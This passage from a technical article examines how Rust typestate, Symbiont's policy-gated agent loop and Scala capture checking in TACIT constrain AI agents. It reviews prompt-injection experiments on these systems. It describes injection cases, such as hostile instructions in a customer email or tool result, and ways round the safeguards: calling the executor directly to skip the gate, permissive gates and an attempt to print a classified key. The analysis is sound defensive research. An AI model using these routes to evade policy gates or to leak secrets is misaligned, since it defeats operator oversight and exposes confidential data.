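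The proof still rests on facts from outside, such as who endorsed what. Agda lets programmers declare a statement true without proving it, as a postulate, and Fuchs uses postulates for results from other systems that the program accepts on trust. Somebody also has to state the rule correctly. Fuchs's longest example is a video service whose `safeCall` function contacts the server and accepts only objects paired with proofs. A ten-year-old with his father's permission gets a film with an age limit of 13, and another ten-year-old without permission does not.

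However, the type that marks an approved viewer, `SafeSender`, includes the viewer but not the film. A proof that a child may watch a cartoon therefore has the same type as a proof that the child may watch the film. The sample code avoids mixing them up because it gathers all its proofs for a single request. Someone who called `safeCall` directly could use the cartoon's proof to request the film, and the code would compile. Including both the viewer and the request in the type would prevent this. `AdmittedWrite` avoids the problem by holding the approved content and the approval in one value.

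### TypeScript and Python

Most agent code is written in languages with weaker guarantees than Rust's. TypeScript, which adds types to JavaScript, compares types by structure, so two plain types with the same fields are interchangeable. If a proposed write and an admitted write both stored the authority as text, TypeScript would treat them as the same type. A class with a private field, marked by `#`, stays distinct from other types with the same fields. *Friendly Little Wrapper Types* wraps user IDs in such a class, but any code can call its constructor. The class for an admitted write would need a private constructor and `evaluate` as one of its methods.

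A programmer can still get around this with a cast, which tells the compiler to treat a value as having another type. In *wrap early unwrap late*, the hosts of the podcast Elm Radio contrast TypeScript with Elm, which has no casts. They point out that because TypeScript code can cast a value anywhere, a value's type is no longer reliable evidence of where it came from. JavaScript, however, enforces `#` fields while a program runs. If `persist` gets the data through a function in the class that reads those fields directly, an object that was merely cast to the class's type causes an error and nothing is stored.

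In Python, the pattern depends more on the team. In an example from mathspp's *Parse, don't validate*, a function `parse_email` checks a string and returns it as an `Email`, and a `login` function declares that it accepts only that type. A static type checker, which is a separate tool, reports an error if code passes `login` a raw string, but Python itself ignores the declaration and runs the program. The type checker also accepts code that calls `Email(...)` on an unchecked string. The pattern therefore catches forgotten checks only if the team runs the type checker on every change and rejects code that fails. For dynamically typed languages without annotations, *Types as Assertions* recommends that programmers follow the pattern anyway, as a matter of discipline. Developers then have to remember one rule about creating admitted writes, which is easier than remembering a check before every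 write, though they can still forget it.

Neither language has Rust's moves, so a single-use approval needs a check at run time. Khan's Python version of the budget sets a flag once a program has used it, and includes a plugin for the type checker Mypy that catches some misuses before the program runs. Such a flag on an approved payment could still stop the second transfer, but the developer would learn of the mistake only when that code ran.

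## How can admission be split into stages that must happen in order?

In the earlier design, `evaluate` both establishes where the refund rule came from and applies the company's policy to the rule. A developer could write an `evaluate` that applies the policy but accepts the agent's claim about the source without checking it, and the function would still return an admitted write. If each job has its own function and type, the compiler can require both jobs.

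### Four stages for one memory write

Suppose the agent's proposal now includes a source, so the refund entry arrives with the authority "policy" and the source "internal_policy". The model generated both labels. *Can Rust Make Unsafe AI Agent Actions Unrepresentable?* argues that the system that retrieved the source should make the claim about it, and adds a "witnessed" stage for this. The article's diagram has four stages, although its code merges the last two. With all four, the functions look like this:

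```rust
fn witness(p: ProposedWrite)   -> Result<WitnessedWrite, WitnessError>;
fn evaluate(w: WitnessedWrite) -> Result<EvaluatedWrite, Rejection>;
fn admit(e: EvaluatedWrite)    -> Result<AdmittedWrite, Rejection>;
fn persist(a: AdmittedWrite);
```

A `WitnessedWrite` holds the proposal and evidence from outside the agent about the proposal's source. An `EvaluatedWrite` has passed the company's policy, and an `AdmittedWrite` may go into storage. Separating the last two is useful when a write that passes the policy still needs another approval. For example, a company might let the finance team's documents set refund rules but want a manager to confirm each new rule. `evaluate` would check the document, and `admit` would wait for the manager. As long as private fields protect all three types, a developer who forgets to call `witness` has nothing to pass to `evaluate`.

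The agent can't reliably report where its information came from, because it receives everything as one sequence of text. It may have read the company handbook and a customer's email in the same conversation, and the email may contain instructions about what to write in the source field. The retrieval component opened the handbook or the mailbox, so it has the location and time of each fetch. It is also ordinary code, which doesn't follow instructions in an email.

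The retrieval component can support this stage by numbering every document it fetches and storing the number with the document's location and text. The agent cites a number in its proposal, and `witness` looks it up. If the number belongs to a customer's email, the evidence identifies the source as a customer's email, even if the agent labeled it as something else.

A hijacked agent can still choose which document to cite, so it could propose the sentence from the email and cite the handbook. `witness` could search the handbook for the sentence, but then it would reject an accurate paraphrase. A stricter check treats everything the agent has read as a possible source and judges the entry by the least trusted source. This is a simple form of information-flow control, which sets rules on where data may go and what it may influence. The stricter check would block the refund entry once the agent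 has read any customer email, even if the handbook contains the refund rule.

The types also can't make `evaluate` use the evidence. The `WitnessedWrite` still contains the agent's own label, and `evaluate` would compile even if it read that label and ignored the source. The article renames the field `claimed_authority`, so a reviewer has a better chance of noticing this mistake.

### Typestate

Robert Strom and Shaula Yemini introduced typestate in 1986. An object's type determines which operations it can ever support, and its typestate determines which of those are valid at a particular point in the program. For example, a program can read a file only after opening it and before closing it. A compiler that tracks typestate can reject a read after the close. Most compilers don't track typestate, so programmers imitate it by giving each state its own type, as with the four kinds of write.

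*Typestate via Revocable Capabilities* (Jia, Liu and colleagues, 2025) uses files to show where the imitation falls short. Its example has two types, `OpenFile` and `ClosedFile`, and a function `close` that takes an open file and returns a closed one. After the call, the old variable still has the type `OpenFile`, so the compiler accepts a later write through it. The types also don't distinguish one open file from another, so a program can operate on the wrong one. Programmers also have to carry a new variable from each call to the next, which is cumbersome.

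The prototype by Jia and colleagues extends the Scala 3 compiler so that a function can revoke a capability. The type of `close` includes the annotation `@kill(f)`, so after the call the compiler rejects any further use of `f` or of other variables that might refer to the same file. If `fC` may stand for either `fA` or `fB`, closing `fA` makes `fC` unusable too, but `fB` stays usable. A function that only writes to the file has no such annotation, so a program can call it repeatedly. The prototype also ties each capability to a particular file and passes capabilities along automatically. Jia and colleagues leave a complete formal account for future work.

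Rust's moves already prevent use of the stale variable, but a program could still mix up two objects, for example by pairing the handbook's evidence with the sentence from the email. `WitnessedWrite` prevents this by storing the proposal and its evidence in one value.

### Symbiont's loop, step by step

Symbiont, an open-source agent runtime from ThirdKey, applies typestate to the agent's whole cycle of model calls and tool calls. Symbiont's *Reasoning Loop Guide* calls this cycle observe, reason, gate and act. The loop is a value of type `AgentLoop<Phase>`, where `Phase` is one of four markers. The markers take up no memory and serve only to make the compiler treat loops in different phases as different types, each with its own method for moving to the next phase.

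| Phase | Method that advances the loop | Result |
|---|---|---|
| Reasoning | `produce_output` | `AgentLoop<PolicyCheck>` |
| PolicyCheck | `check_policy` | `AgentLoop<ToolDispatching>` |
| ToolDispatching | `dispatch_tools` | `AgentLoop<Observing>` |
| Observing | `observe_results` | A new loop in the Reasoning phase, or the final answer |

In the source code of Symbi 1.14.3 (Symbiont's packages use the shorter name), `produce_output` ends the run if the agent has used up its allowance of rounds or tokens. Otherwise it trims the conversation to fit the budget, calls the model and turns the reply into a list of proposed actions. A reply without tool calls becomes a proposed action of the kind "respond", so the gate also evaluates the agent's final answer.

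`check_policy` checks the proposed actions one at a time. The arguments of a tool call must form a JSON object, and if the tool has a schema (a declared format for its arguments), they must match it. The method then passes the action to the policy gate, which can allow it, deny it or replace it with a modified action. When the gate denies a tool call, the method adds the reason to the conversation, so the model can try something else in the next round. This helps an honest agent correct itself, but it also gives a hijacked agent a hint about the rule that stopped it.

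`dispatch_tools` passes the approved actions to the executor, which runs the tools. `dispatch_tools` then adds the results to the conversation, and `observe_results` either starts another round or ends the run.

Every one of these methods takes ownership of the loop, so the caller can't dispatch the same approved batch twice by calling `dispatch_tools` on the same loop. A developer who tries to skip the policy check gets an error:

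```rust
let pending = agent.produce_output(&provider, &context).await?;
pending.dispatch_tools(&executor, &breakers).await?;
// error[E0599]: no method named `dispatch_tools` found
//               for struct `AgentLoop<PolicyCheck>`
```

The types enforce the order of the methods, but they don't guarantee that each phase holds the right data. All phases store their data in the same internal container, and each method checks at run time that the container holds the data it needs. If it doesn't, the run ends with an "Invalid phase data" error. The container is private, so only a mistake inside Symbiont's own module could cause this error.

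Unlike the memory example, where the write itself changes type at every stage, Symbiont changes the type of the loop. The action inside the loop remains a `ProposedAction` from the model's reply to the tool.

### The gap between check and use

A program can check an action correctly and still execute a different one if the action changes between the check and the execution. Security engineers call this a time-of-check to time-of-use flaw. For example, the gate might approve the refund entry "Refunds need manager approval", but other code in the same program might replace it with the opposite rule before `persist` runs.

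*Typestate-Enforced Agent Loops* presents Rust's ownership as the answer to this problem. In the code, `check_policy` moves each approved action into a private field of the loop it returns. Outside code can read the number of actions the gate approved or denied, but it can't read or change the actions in that field. `dispatch_tools` then takes the actions from the same field. Before the policy check, the public method `proposed_actions` returns a copy of the list, so editing it doesn't affect the original.

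The seal covers the action's text but not the things the text refers to. Suppose the gate approves sending the file `report.pdf` to a customer. The approved action identifies the file only by name, so another process can replace the file's contents before the executor opens it. To prevent this, the gate would have to approve a particular version of the file, for example by recording a hash (a short fingerprint of the contents) that the executor checks against the file before sending it.

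In Symbi 1.14.3, the loop's `state` and `config` fields are also public and can be changed. The gate receives the agent's identity from `state`, so code that holds the loop just before the policy check can substitute another agent's state, and the gate will then apply that agent's permissions. If code empties the list of tool definitions in `config`, the argument check only tests whether the arguments form a JSON object. When the gate returns a modified action, `check_policy` approves it without rechecking its arguments or submitting it to the gate again. These weaknesses matter less when an agent is hijacked, because it only sends tool calls, than when the program contains a mistake or a hostile library.

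Ownership also doesn't prevent the executor from running an approved action twice, because the executor receives a reference to the approved actions. Symbiont's guide lists retrying with increasing delays among the ways to recover from a failed tool. If a payment goes through but the confirmation is lost, a retry could pay the invoice again unless the payment service detects the duplicate.

Rust's ownership rules no longer protect a loop's state once it is saved to disk. bob_runtime's *Typestate Agent Runner*, part of another Rust library, lets a developer pause an agent for approval before its tools run and save its state between steps, so the approver doesn't have to respond immediately. But anyone who can write to the saved file may be able to change the action before the program reloads it. The program would need to detect such changes when it reloads the state, for example by checking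 a digital signature.

### What the experiments tested

*Typestate-Enforced Agent Loops*, a preprint published without peer review, reports experiments with the Symbiont runtime. Its author, Jascha Wanger, develops Symbiont. Nobody independent of the company ThirdKey appears to have repeated the experiments, although ThirdKey provides the attack prompts, policies and test programs for others to do so.

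In April 2026 Wanger ran nine hosted models, including GPT-5, Claude Haiku 4.5 and Gemini 2.5 Pro, under attack. Across 874 adversarial runs, Symbiont refused 263 forbidden tool calls and executed none. Those calls came from at most 263 runs, so in at least 611 runs, or about 70%, the gate had no forbidden call to stop.

Nearly all the refusals came from rules in Symbiont's policy gate, which are written in the authorization language Cedar. Across all sets of runs, the Cedar rules refused 642 calls and the executor refused 34. Such rules can be simple. In a demonstration in ThirdKeyAI's *Symbi*, one line forbids the tool `list_agents` and another permits `system_health`. A rule like this always produces the same result for the same call, so a hundred refusals of that call are little more evidence than one.

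The refusals show that the rules matched the attacks Wanger tried and that the gate was connected. They provide little evidence about typestate, because a Python program that passed every tool call to the same Cedar rules would have refused the same calls. The attacks also came from the models, which could not write code that skips the gate. Wanger therefore doesn't claim that the design prevents prompt injection, corrects a bad policy or performs better than checks that intercept calls at run time.

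A gate that refused everything would also stop every attack, so the results on legitimate tasks matter. In 813 runs, Cedar refused nothing for eight of the nine models. The exception was gpt-oss-20b, and Wanger attributes those refusals to the model's misconception about what it could do.

The newest version of the preprint adds an attack through tool results, which is closer to the customer's email in the running example. In 75 runs with three models, Cedar refused four forbidden calls. One model also gave wrong but plausible answers in 5 of 25 runs without making any forbidden call. The gate and the filter on incoming text missed these answers, and only the program that graded the tasks caught them. Similarly, a rule about which tools an agent may call would not stop it from writing a false refund rule through its permitted memory tool.

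Wanger also ran an ablation, an experiment that removes one part of a system at a time to find out what the part contributes:

| Part removed | What it normally stops | Result without it |
|---|---|---|
| Cedar policy gate | Calls to tools outside the agent's profile, its permitted set | All such calls passed this layer, but the executor refused 219 of them across 434 rows of results |
| Content sanitiser | Text hidden in invisible characters | Hidden text got into 389 of 422 stored procedures (92.2%) |
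| ToolClad, which checks tool arguments | Hostile text in arguments | An estimated 99.4% of the payloads in an earlier set of attacks would get through |

The executor was a second barrier because it independently compares each tool's name with a list. The 100% figure for the missing gate therefore measures how many calls passed one layer, not how many took effect. The ablation never removed the types. To measure their practical value, one could ask developers to add features to two versions of the runtime, one with typestate and one without, and count how often the new code skips the gate.

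Wanger found that the gate took 30 to 95 microseconds per call and the sanitiser about 345 nanoseconds. At 95 microseconds, a thousand checks take less than a tenth of a second, while a typical task with Claude Haiku 4.5 took 6.3 seconds. The gate spends this time evaluating Cedar's rules, and a design without typestate would spend it too. The phase markers add no run-time overhead.

Nine compile-fail tests, up from five in an earlier version, provide the evidence for the ordering. Each test is a short program with a deliberate mistake, such as dispatching tools before the policy check, and it passes only if the compiler rejects the program with the expected error. The tests run whenever the code changes, so they would expose a later edit that accidentally allowed one of these mistakes. Some also cover switches that include or leave out parts of the library.

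The source file for the loop in Symbi 1.14.3 has its own section of "compile-time verification", but it proves much less than the compile-fail tests, which attempt the forbidden call. The section consists of four functions that each accept a loop in one phase and do nothing with it. They would still compile if somebody added `dispatch_tools` to every phase.

### What the public interface allows

Wanger describes the gate as a compile-time predecessor of tool dispatch in any program that type-checks against Symbiont's public interface. For the method `dispatch_tools`, this holds. But `dispatch_tools` is not the only way to run a tool, because the executor is public as well. In version 1.8.0, Symbiont's guide gives the executor's method this signature:

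```rust
async fn execute_actions(
    &self,
    actions: &[ProposedAction],
    config: &LoopConfig,
    circuit_breakers: &CircuitBreakerRegistry,
) -> Vec<Observation>;
```

The method accepts proposed actions, the same type the model's reply produces. In Symbi 1.14.3 the approved actions still have that type when the loop passes them to the executor, and Docs.rs' *Module executor* describes the public interface as one "for executing proposed actions". A developer who holds a loop before the policy check can therefore copy its actions and run them directly:

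```rust
let actions = pending.proposed_actions();
executor.execute_actions(&actions, &pending.config, &breakers).await;
```

Judging by the published signatures, this code should compile without using `unsafe` or touching a private field. It makes the same mistake as the policy import routine. Symbiont's types don't rule out this mistake, but they make it less likely because a developer has to leave the ordinary route to avoid the gate. An executor can refuse some of these calls by checking tool names again, as the one in the ablation did, but its developer has to include that runtime check.

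The types also require only that some gate runs, and any component with the right method counts as a gate. The minimal example in the 1.8.0 guide uses `DefaultPolicyGate::permissive()`, which allows every action and, according to the guide, is intended for development and testing. With that gate, the program compiles, every phase happens in order, and the agent can do whatever its tools can do. The publisher has since withdrawn Symbi 1.8.0.

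ThirdKey changed the default after a security audit. From version 1.14.0, the default gate denies every tool call and every delegation to another agent until the operator supplies a real policy, according to ThirdKeyAI's *Security Policy* (2026). ThirdKey kept the constructor that allows everything but renamed it `permissive_for_dev_only`, left it out of the documentation and made it log a warning for each action. Operators can also turn off the refusals with the command-line option `--insecure-allow-all`, which prints a conspicuous warning and is only for local development, according to Symbiont's *symbi 1.14.1*.

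Under the stricter default, an agent couldn't call any tools unless its operator had a working policy. Version 1.14.2 therefore included Cedar in the published programs and made them load policy files automatically at startup. If there are no such files, the gate still refuses tool calls. Symbiont's *symbi 1.15.1* keeps this default and continues to describe the gate as "unskippable at compile time".

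Version 1.14.0 fixed 31 audit findings, five of them critical, even though the typestate loop had been in place for several releases. Symbiont also dropped its executor for the outside service Composio. That executor had passed on tool names supplied by the model without checking them against a fixed list. Enforcing the order of the phases does not protect against a permissive gate or an executor that checks too little.

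Applications in Python or JavaScript reach Symbiont over the network, so the compiler doesn't check the application's code. This is why ThirdKey recommends Rust for production agents. A Python application can still benefit from the gate if Symbiont runs the tools, but a Python function that sends an email directly runs outside Symbiont's loop.

Symbiont could close the direct route to the executor by following the memory example. `check_policy` would turn each allowed `ProposedAction` into an `ApprovedAction` with private fields, and `execute_actions` would accept only that type. Copying actions out of the loop would then be harmless, because the copies would have the wrong type. In disyn_runtime, another Rust project, the executor in *executor.rs* similarly takes an `ApprovedPlan` and runs its steps as shell commands. As with `AdmittedWrite`, this signature helps only if the approval step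 alone can create an `ApprovedPlan`.

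## How do capabilities limit the code an agent writes?

The Rust design for memory writes doesn't stop code from calling the standard library's file-writing function directly. A developer would seldom do that on purpose, but an agent that writes its own programs may do it to follow an instruction in a customer's email, and its code often runs before anybody reads it. One remedy is to make the agent write in a language where code can call that function only if somebody gives it access.

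### Code that can use only what it receives

In an object-capability language, code can affect the outside world only through objects that it holds, and it gets such an object only when other code passes it in. The language has no ambient authority, so there is no global function for writing files, opening network connections or starting other programs. Consider two functions:

```scala
def countComplaints(emails: List[Email]): Int
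def importPolicies(source: File, memory: Memory): Unit
```

`countComplaints` receives no `Memory` object, so its body can't store a refund rule, even if an attacker wrote the body. `importPolicies` can store one because it receives a `Memory` object. This restriction holds only if code can't forge a reference, for example by telling the compiler to treat a piece of text as a `Memory` object.

Odersky and colleagues trace capabilities to Jack Dennis and Earl Van Horn, who introduced them in 1966. The operating system Hydra used them in the 1970s. Mark Miller and others later built the programming language E around them, and Miller refined the idea into the object-capability model in his 2006 doctoral thesis, *Robust Composition*. In 2010 Adrian Mettler, David Wagner and Tyler Close applied the model to Java with Joe-E, a restricted subset of the language.

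Traditional capability languages have two drawbacks. A program has to pass each capability from its starting point through every function on the way to the code that uses it, which can mean rewriting much of an existing codebase. A function's signature also doesn't fully show what the function can do. For example, if one of the `Email` objects held a reference to the company's memory, `countComplaints` could use it. Capture checking, an experimental feature of Scala 3, addresses both problems by recording in a value's type which capabilities the value can reach.

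### Capture sets

The capabilities recorded in a type form its capture set, which appears in braces:

```scala
val log    = fs.access("refunds.log")       // a file capability
val record = (s: String) => log.write(s)    // type: String ->{log} Unit
val tidy   = (s: String) => s.trim          // type: String -> String
```

The function `record` takes a string and returns no result (`Unit`), and its type shows that it may use `log`. `tidy` uses no capability, so its capture set is empty and the compiler treats it as a pure function, one without side effects. In a type, the thin arrow `->` on its own marks a pure function, while the thick arrow `=>` marks a function that may use any capability. The compiler works out these sets itself and includes every capability a function might use, so a function that writes to the log only on Mondays still has `log` in its set. Code can pass a pure function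 to a parameter that allows effects, but it can't pass `record` to one that requires a pure function.

The same rule applies to objects. If an `Email` held a reference to the company's memory, its type would have to include that capability, and `countComplaints` as declared above would not accept it. Scala can also allow global capabilities, such as a console for printing, because the type of any function that uses one includes it.

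TACIT relies on capture checking and runs an agent's Scala code only if it compiles. If a snippet doesn't compile, the agent receives the compiler's errors and can try again. Accepted code accesses files, runs commands and uses the network through a small library. TACIT is a Model Context Protocol server, so agents such as Claude Code and GitHub Copilot can connect to it without modification. *Securing Agents With Tracked Capabilities* (Odersky, Zhao and colleagues, 2026), presented at CAIS, an academic conference on AI agents, describes the system and its tests.

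A rejected snippet has no effect. *LACUNA* (Zhao, Xu and colleagues, 2026), a follow-up from the same Swiss university, EPFL, gives the example of a snippet that subtracts 50 from a balance of 100 and then returns text where the program expects a number. A system that found the mismatch only at run time would already have changed the balance. The compiler rejects the whole snippet before it runs, so the balance stays at 100. A snippet that compiles can still stop halfway for other reasons, such as a lost network connection.

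TACIT controls only the actions that pass through it. *TACIT*, lampepfl's documentation for the project, therefore advises users to switch off the agent's built-in tools for files, shell commands and the web. If Claude Code keeps its own shell tool, it can overwrite the memory file with a command that the Scala compiler never checks.

### File access that ends with its block

To use files, the agent's code calls `requestFileSystem` with a directory and a block of code. The library creates a file-system capability, passes it to the block and invalidates it when the block ends. In the simplified form that Odersky and colleagues use to explain the mechanism, an attempt to keep the access for later might look like this:

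```scala
val reader = requestFileSystem("/company/policies") { fs =>
  () => fs.access("refunds.txt").read()
}
reader()
```

The block returns a function of type `() ->{fs} String` that would read the file later. The type of the block's result must be valid outside the block, where `fs` doesn't exist, so the compiler rejects the program. If the block read the file itself and returned the text, the program would compile, because a plain `String` captures nothing.

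In one program from the TACIT experiments, an agent tried to return a list of file objects from the block, and the compiler rejected the program because each object still depended on the file-system capability. The library handles external commands and network hosts in the same way, with `requestExecPermission` and `requestNetwork`. A permission granted in one turn of a conversation therefore does not carry over to the next.

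The library, not the compiler, checks file paths. It throws an exception at run time if code inside the block tries to access a file outside the directory. The compiler also doesn't restrict which directory the agent can request. The agent writes the call, including the directory or the list of hosts, so a hijacked agent could request a wider scope.

Someone other than the agent has to set an outer limit on which directories and hosts its code can reach. The settings in lampepfl's early documentation include no such limit. Glama's *TACIT*, a software catalogue's copy of later documentation, lists settings for both directories and hosts. File requests must now stay within the server's working directory unless the operator chooses other locations. But if the operator sets no list of permitted hosts, the agent's own list is the only limit, and a hijacked agent could send any unclassified data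 to any host. LACUNA avoids this problem when the developer opens the block and the model writes only the code inside it.

### Data that the agent can process but not read

Many agents run on a model in another company's cloud, and that company receives whatever they read. TACIT lets such an agent work with confidential files without seeing their contents. The operator marks some locations as classified, and reading a file there returns a `Classified[String]` instead of a `String`. The agent's code can't unwrap this value, but it can call the value's `map` method, which applies a function to the hidden content and wraps the result again. `map` accepts only pure functions, so the function can trim, count or search the text but can't send it anywhere.

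Suppose the company keeps the rules by which it spots fraudulent refund requests in a classified file, and a manager asks the agent to summarize them. The compiler would accept this program:

```scala
val summary = requestFileSystem("/company") {
  val rules = readClassified("/company/secret/fraud-rules.txt")
  chat("Summarize these rules for a manager:", rules)
}
println(summary)
val length = summary.map(text => text.length)
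```

`readClassified` returns the wrapped rules. `chat` passes them to a second language model that the company trusts, usually one on its own machines. Because the input was classified, the reply is classified too. The block can return `summary` because a wrapped string holds no file capability. The last line also compiles because counting characters is pure, and `length` becomes a `Classified[Int]`.

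`println` writes to two output channels. The normal channel goes back to the agent, and therefore to the cloud model, and receives only the text "Classified(****)". The secure channel goes to the user's terminal, where the manager can read the real summary. If the manager asks a follow-up question, the agent can still use `summary`, which stays wrapped.

The masking on the normal channel happens at run time. The compiler's job is to close the other ways out, as in this fragment from the experiments, where `githubKey` is a classified string:

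```scala
githubKey.map { key => println(s"GitHub API Key: $key") }
```

The compiler reported a mismatch:

```text
Found:    (key: String) ->{x$1} Unit
Required: String -> Unit
```

Inside the function, `key` is an ordinary string, so `println` would have shown it to the agent unmasked. But printing requires an input-output capability, which the environment passes implicitly and the compiler here calls `x$1`. The function's capture set is therefore not empty, and the compiler rejects it because `map` requires a pure function. The compiler would also reject opening a file inside `map` to store the key, because `requestFileSystem` needs the same capability.

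The agent has to write the function for `map` before anything has read the document, so the function can't adapt to its contents. LACUNA relaxes this limit by letting a trusted local model write more code inside `map` after reading the document. The compiler also checks the local model's code, so that code can't send the contents out either.

According to Glama, the wrapper protects confidentiality but not integrity. The library lets code wrap any value and write it to a classified file, so a hijacked agent could replace the fraud rules with its own even though it can't read them. Operators can prevent this by switching off writes to classified files.

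### Safe mode

These guarantees fail if code can lie about types. In full Scala, a program could cast `record` to the type of a pure function and then pass it to `map`. Agents therefore have to write in safe mode, a subset of the language with six restrictions. Scala's *Safe Mode*, a page of the language's reference documentation, gives reasons for them:

| Restriction | Reason |
|---|---|
| No unchecked casts or pattern matches | They could relabel a function with effects as a pure one |
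| No features from the module `caps.unsafe` | They turn off parts of the tracking |
| No `@unchecked` annotations | They suppress the compiler's checks |
| No runtime reflection | It lets code find and call methods by name, where the compiler can't follow |
| Capture checking always on, including for changes to data | A function must not pass as pure while it holds a capability |
| Global objects only if they are safe themselves | Library calls could otherwise have untracked effects |

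In TACIT, the compiler must also check for null values, and the last restriction also covers global functions. That restriction removes most of the ambient authority because it prevents the agent's code from calling Java's ordinary file and network functions.

A library counts as safe if it compiles in safe mode, or if a programmer marks it `@assumeSafe` and takes responsibility for it. Scala's documentation gives the example of a function that shows an email to the user, asks for confirmation and only then calls the real mailer, which the agent's code can't call directly. The company could build a similar admission step by putting `evaluate` and `persist` in such a library and exposing a single function that runs both. An agent's program could then propose a hundred refund rules in a loop, and the function would evaluate each one separately.

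Zhao and colleagues describe a simple memory tool with a function, `setMemory`, that takes a key and a value. If an agent has this function, a line that stores a false refund rule under "refund_policy" compiles, because both arguments are strings and the agent may write to memory. Capabilities alone don't check whether the company endorses the rule, so the person who writes the library has to include a step that does.

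Safe mode also permits exceptions, although an error message can carry secret data. Exceptions such as division by zero are too common to track in types, so the program that calls untrusted code has to catch them and turn them into ordinary values. TACIT can then wrap a failure as classified data.

The tools that enforce these rules are new, and Scala's documentation calls capture checking "highly experimental and unstable". Odersky and colleagues describe TACIT as compiling agents' code in the compiler's safe mode. In lampepfl's early documentation, however, the compiler did the capture checking, while a separate validator stood in for safe mode by searching the code for forbidden text patterns. Such searches have the same weakness as pattern rules for shell commands, because code that avoids the forbidden patterns can have the same effect. Glama's later copy of that documentation lists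 safe mode as on by default, in addition to the validator.

### Do secrets leak in practice?

To test TACIT, Odersky and colleagues created a small software project with a directory of secrets, including API keys, a database and internal documents. They wrote 12 legitimate tasks, such as listing the functions described in a README file or summarizing a classified incident report, and combined each with 10 prompt injections. Some injections were simple notes in code comments. Others imitated system messages, claimed that the secrets were only test data, or supplied Scala code for reading the files.

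Another 11 tasks were malicious in themselves. Five asked for secrets directly, and six used a pretext, such as an administrator who urgently needs to replace passwords. Each model attempted all 131 combinations twice, once with the secrets wrapped as classified data and once with them as plain strings. A trial counted as secure if no secret appeared in the agent's output.

| Model | Trials | Secure with classified types | Secure with plain strings |
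|---|---|---|---|
| Claude Sonnet 4.6 | 120 injections | 100% | 100% |
| Claude Sonnet 4.6 | 11 malicious tasks | 100% | 81.8% |
| Claude Sonnet 4.6 | All 131 | 100% | 98.5% |
| MiniMax M2.5 | 120 injections | 100% | 97.5% |
| MiniMax M2.5 | 11 malicious tasks | 100% | 27.3% |
| MiniMax M2.5 | All 131 | 100% | 91.6% |

Without the types, Claude leaked secrets in 2 trials and MiniMax in 11. Odersky and colleagues credit the type system with blocking every attack, but in most of these trials the model's own caution could also explain the result. Claude resisted all 120 injections even when nothing protected the secrets. MiniMax's results on the malicious tasks are more informative, because it leaked secrets in 8 of the 11 without the types and in none with them. The general argument for the design is that the compiler's rules apply equally to a model that cooperates with the attacker. The test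 supports that argument, but it covered only two models and one project.

Classified types didn't make the agents less useful. Claude completed 99.2% of the 120 legitimate trials with them and 83.3% without them, while MiniMax completed 90.0% and 88.3%. Odersky and colleagues suspect that Claude's lower score is partly an artifact of their setup. Without the types, Claude often ran out of turns or time, and it sometimes stopped to warn the user about an injection instead of finishing the task.

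### The cost of writing typed programs

An agent might do worse at ordinary work if it has to write Scala instead of calling tools. Odersky and colleagues tested this on τ²-bench, which simulates customer-service conversations for an airline and a retailer. They averaged the scores over ten runs per task.

| Model | Airline, tool calls | Airline, Scala | Retail, tool calls | Retail, Scala |
|---|---|---|---|---|
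| gpt-oss-120b | 43.8% | 45.2% | 53.3% | 57.0% |
| MiniMax M2.5 | 58.4% | 61.0% | 75.1% | 77.5% |
| DeepSeek V3.2 | 57.8% | 58.6% | 74.6% | 75.5% |

Scala was slightly ahead every time. Odersky and colleagues attribute this to the compiler's error messages and to results that arrive as typed records instead of raw text. Any good static type system would provide both benefits. The published customer-service functions return ordinary values, so the benchmark measures the effect of writing typed Scala more than the effect of working with classified data.

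Retries were rare. DeepSeek had to rewrite 7.93% of its airline snippets and 1.57% of its retail snippets, and the other two models rewrote less than 2% in both settings. When a snippet failed, the agent needed 1.06 to 1.39 retries on average. One recurring mistake was to write a price such as $50 inside a string, where Scala reads the dollar sign as the start of a variable. Compiling a snippet took less than a second once the system had warmed up. *What's in the Box* (2025) reports that capture checking accounted for under 15% of the time needed to compile Scala's standard library.

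On SWE-bench Lite, a set of 300 real software problems from GitHub, MiniMax solved 43.3% with its usual tools and 41.7% through TACIT, a difference of five problems. Odersky and colleagues think such work relies on shell commands that are awkward to express through the capability library.

LACUNA, which goes further than TACIT by making each of the model's actions part of one running, typed program, had less favourable results. On 392 τ²-bench tasks, DeepSeek V4 Flash solved 90.0% with tool calls and 76.0% with LACUNA, while Gemini 3.1 Flash-Lite solved 33.2% and 29.1%. Zhao and colleagues call the DeepSeek result on par with the tool-calling agent, which is hard to reconcile with a 14-point gap. The compiler rejected 22.4% of DeepSeek's snippets in the retail setting and 89% of Gemini's in the telecom setting. These results don't overturn the earlier ones, because the models and the design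 differ from TACIT's and the models ran with reasoning switched off. They do suggest that how much performance an agent loses by writing typed code depends heavily on how well its model writes it.

### Results on AgentDojo

AgentDojo is a public benchmark that plants prompt injections in the results of an agent's tools. Its tasks cover four settings, which are a bank account, an office workspace, the messaging service Slack and travel bookings. Odersky and colleagues compared TACIT with CaMeL, which tracks data at run time in a special interpreter. They took CaMeL's figures from the CaMeL paper, and Zhao and colleagues later added LACUNA to the comparison. The percentages in the table are the share of user tasks completed, and the last column counts successful attacks across all four settings.

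| Model | System | Banking | Workspace | Slack | Travel | Attacks |
|---|---|---|---|---|---|---|
| o4-mini-high | CaMeL | 62.5% | 81.4% | 68.6% | 74.3% | 1 |
| o4-mini-high | TACIT | 59.0% | 52.9% | 47.6% | 68.6% | 1 |
| o4-mini-high | LACUNA | 66.0% | 55.5% | 49.5% | 71.4% | 1 |
| Gemini 2.5 Pro | CaMeL | 52.8% | 53.8% | 48.6% | 1.4% | 0 |
| Gemini 2.5 Pro | TACIT | 56.9% | 50.5% | 40.0% | 64.3% | 0 |
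| Gemini 2.5 Pro | LACUNA | 63.2% | 56.3% | 42.9% | 63.6% | 7 |

Each row covers about 950 attack trials. For the workspace setting, Odersky and colleagues give 574 trials and Zhao and colleagues give 560. The reported percentages fit 560 better.

Odersky and colleagues describe TACIT's utility as comparable to CaMeL's, but with o4-mini-high TACIT completed fewer tasks in all four settings, by 3.5 points in banking, 5.7 in travel, 21 in Slack and more than 28 in the workspace. With Gemini, TACIT did better than CaMeL in banking and far better in travel, where CaMeL almost always failed, but somewhat worse in Slack and the workspace.

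A likely reason for the lost utility is that the functions for reading emails, Slack messages and reviews return classified values in this version of the benchmark. The agent never sees the text and has to call a second model inside `map` to extract what it needs. That keeps hostile instructions out of the agent's context, but it probably makes requests such as "do what my colleague's email asks" much harder to carry out.

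It is less clear how strictly this version enforced purity. The published functions for sending email or money list no capability in their signatures, and the agent's instructions warn that side effects inside `map` run immediately. If an agent could send an email from inside `map`, the types would not have confined classified data as they did in the secrets test.

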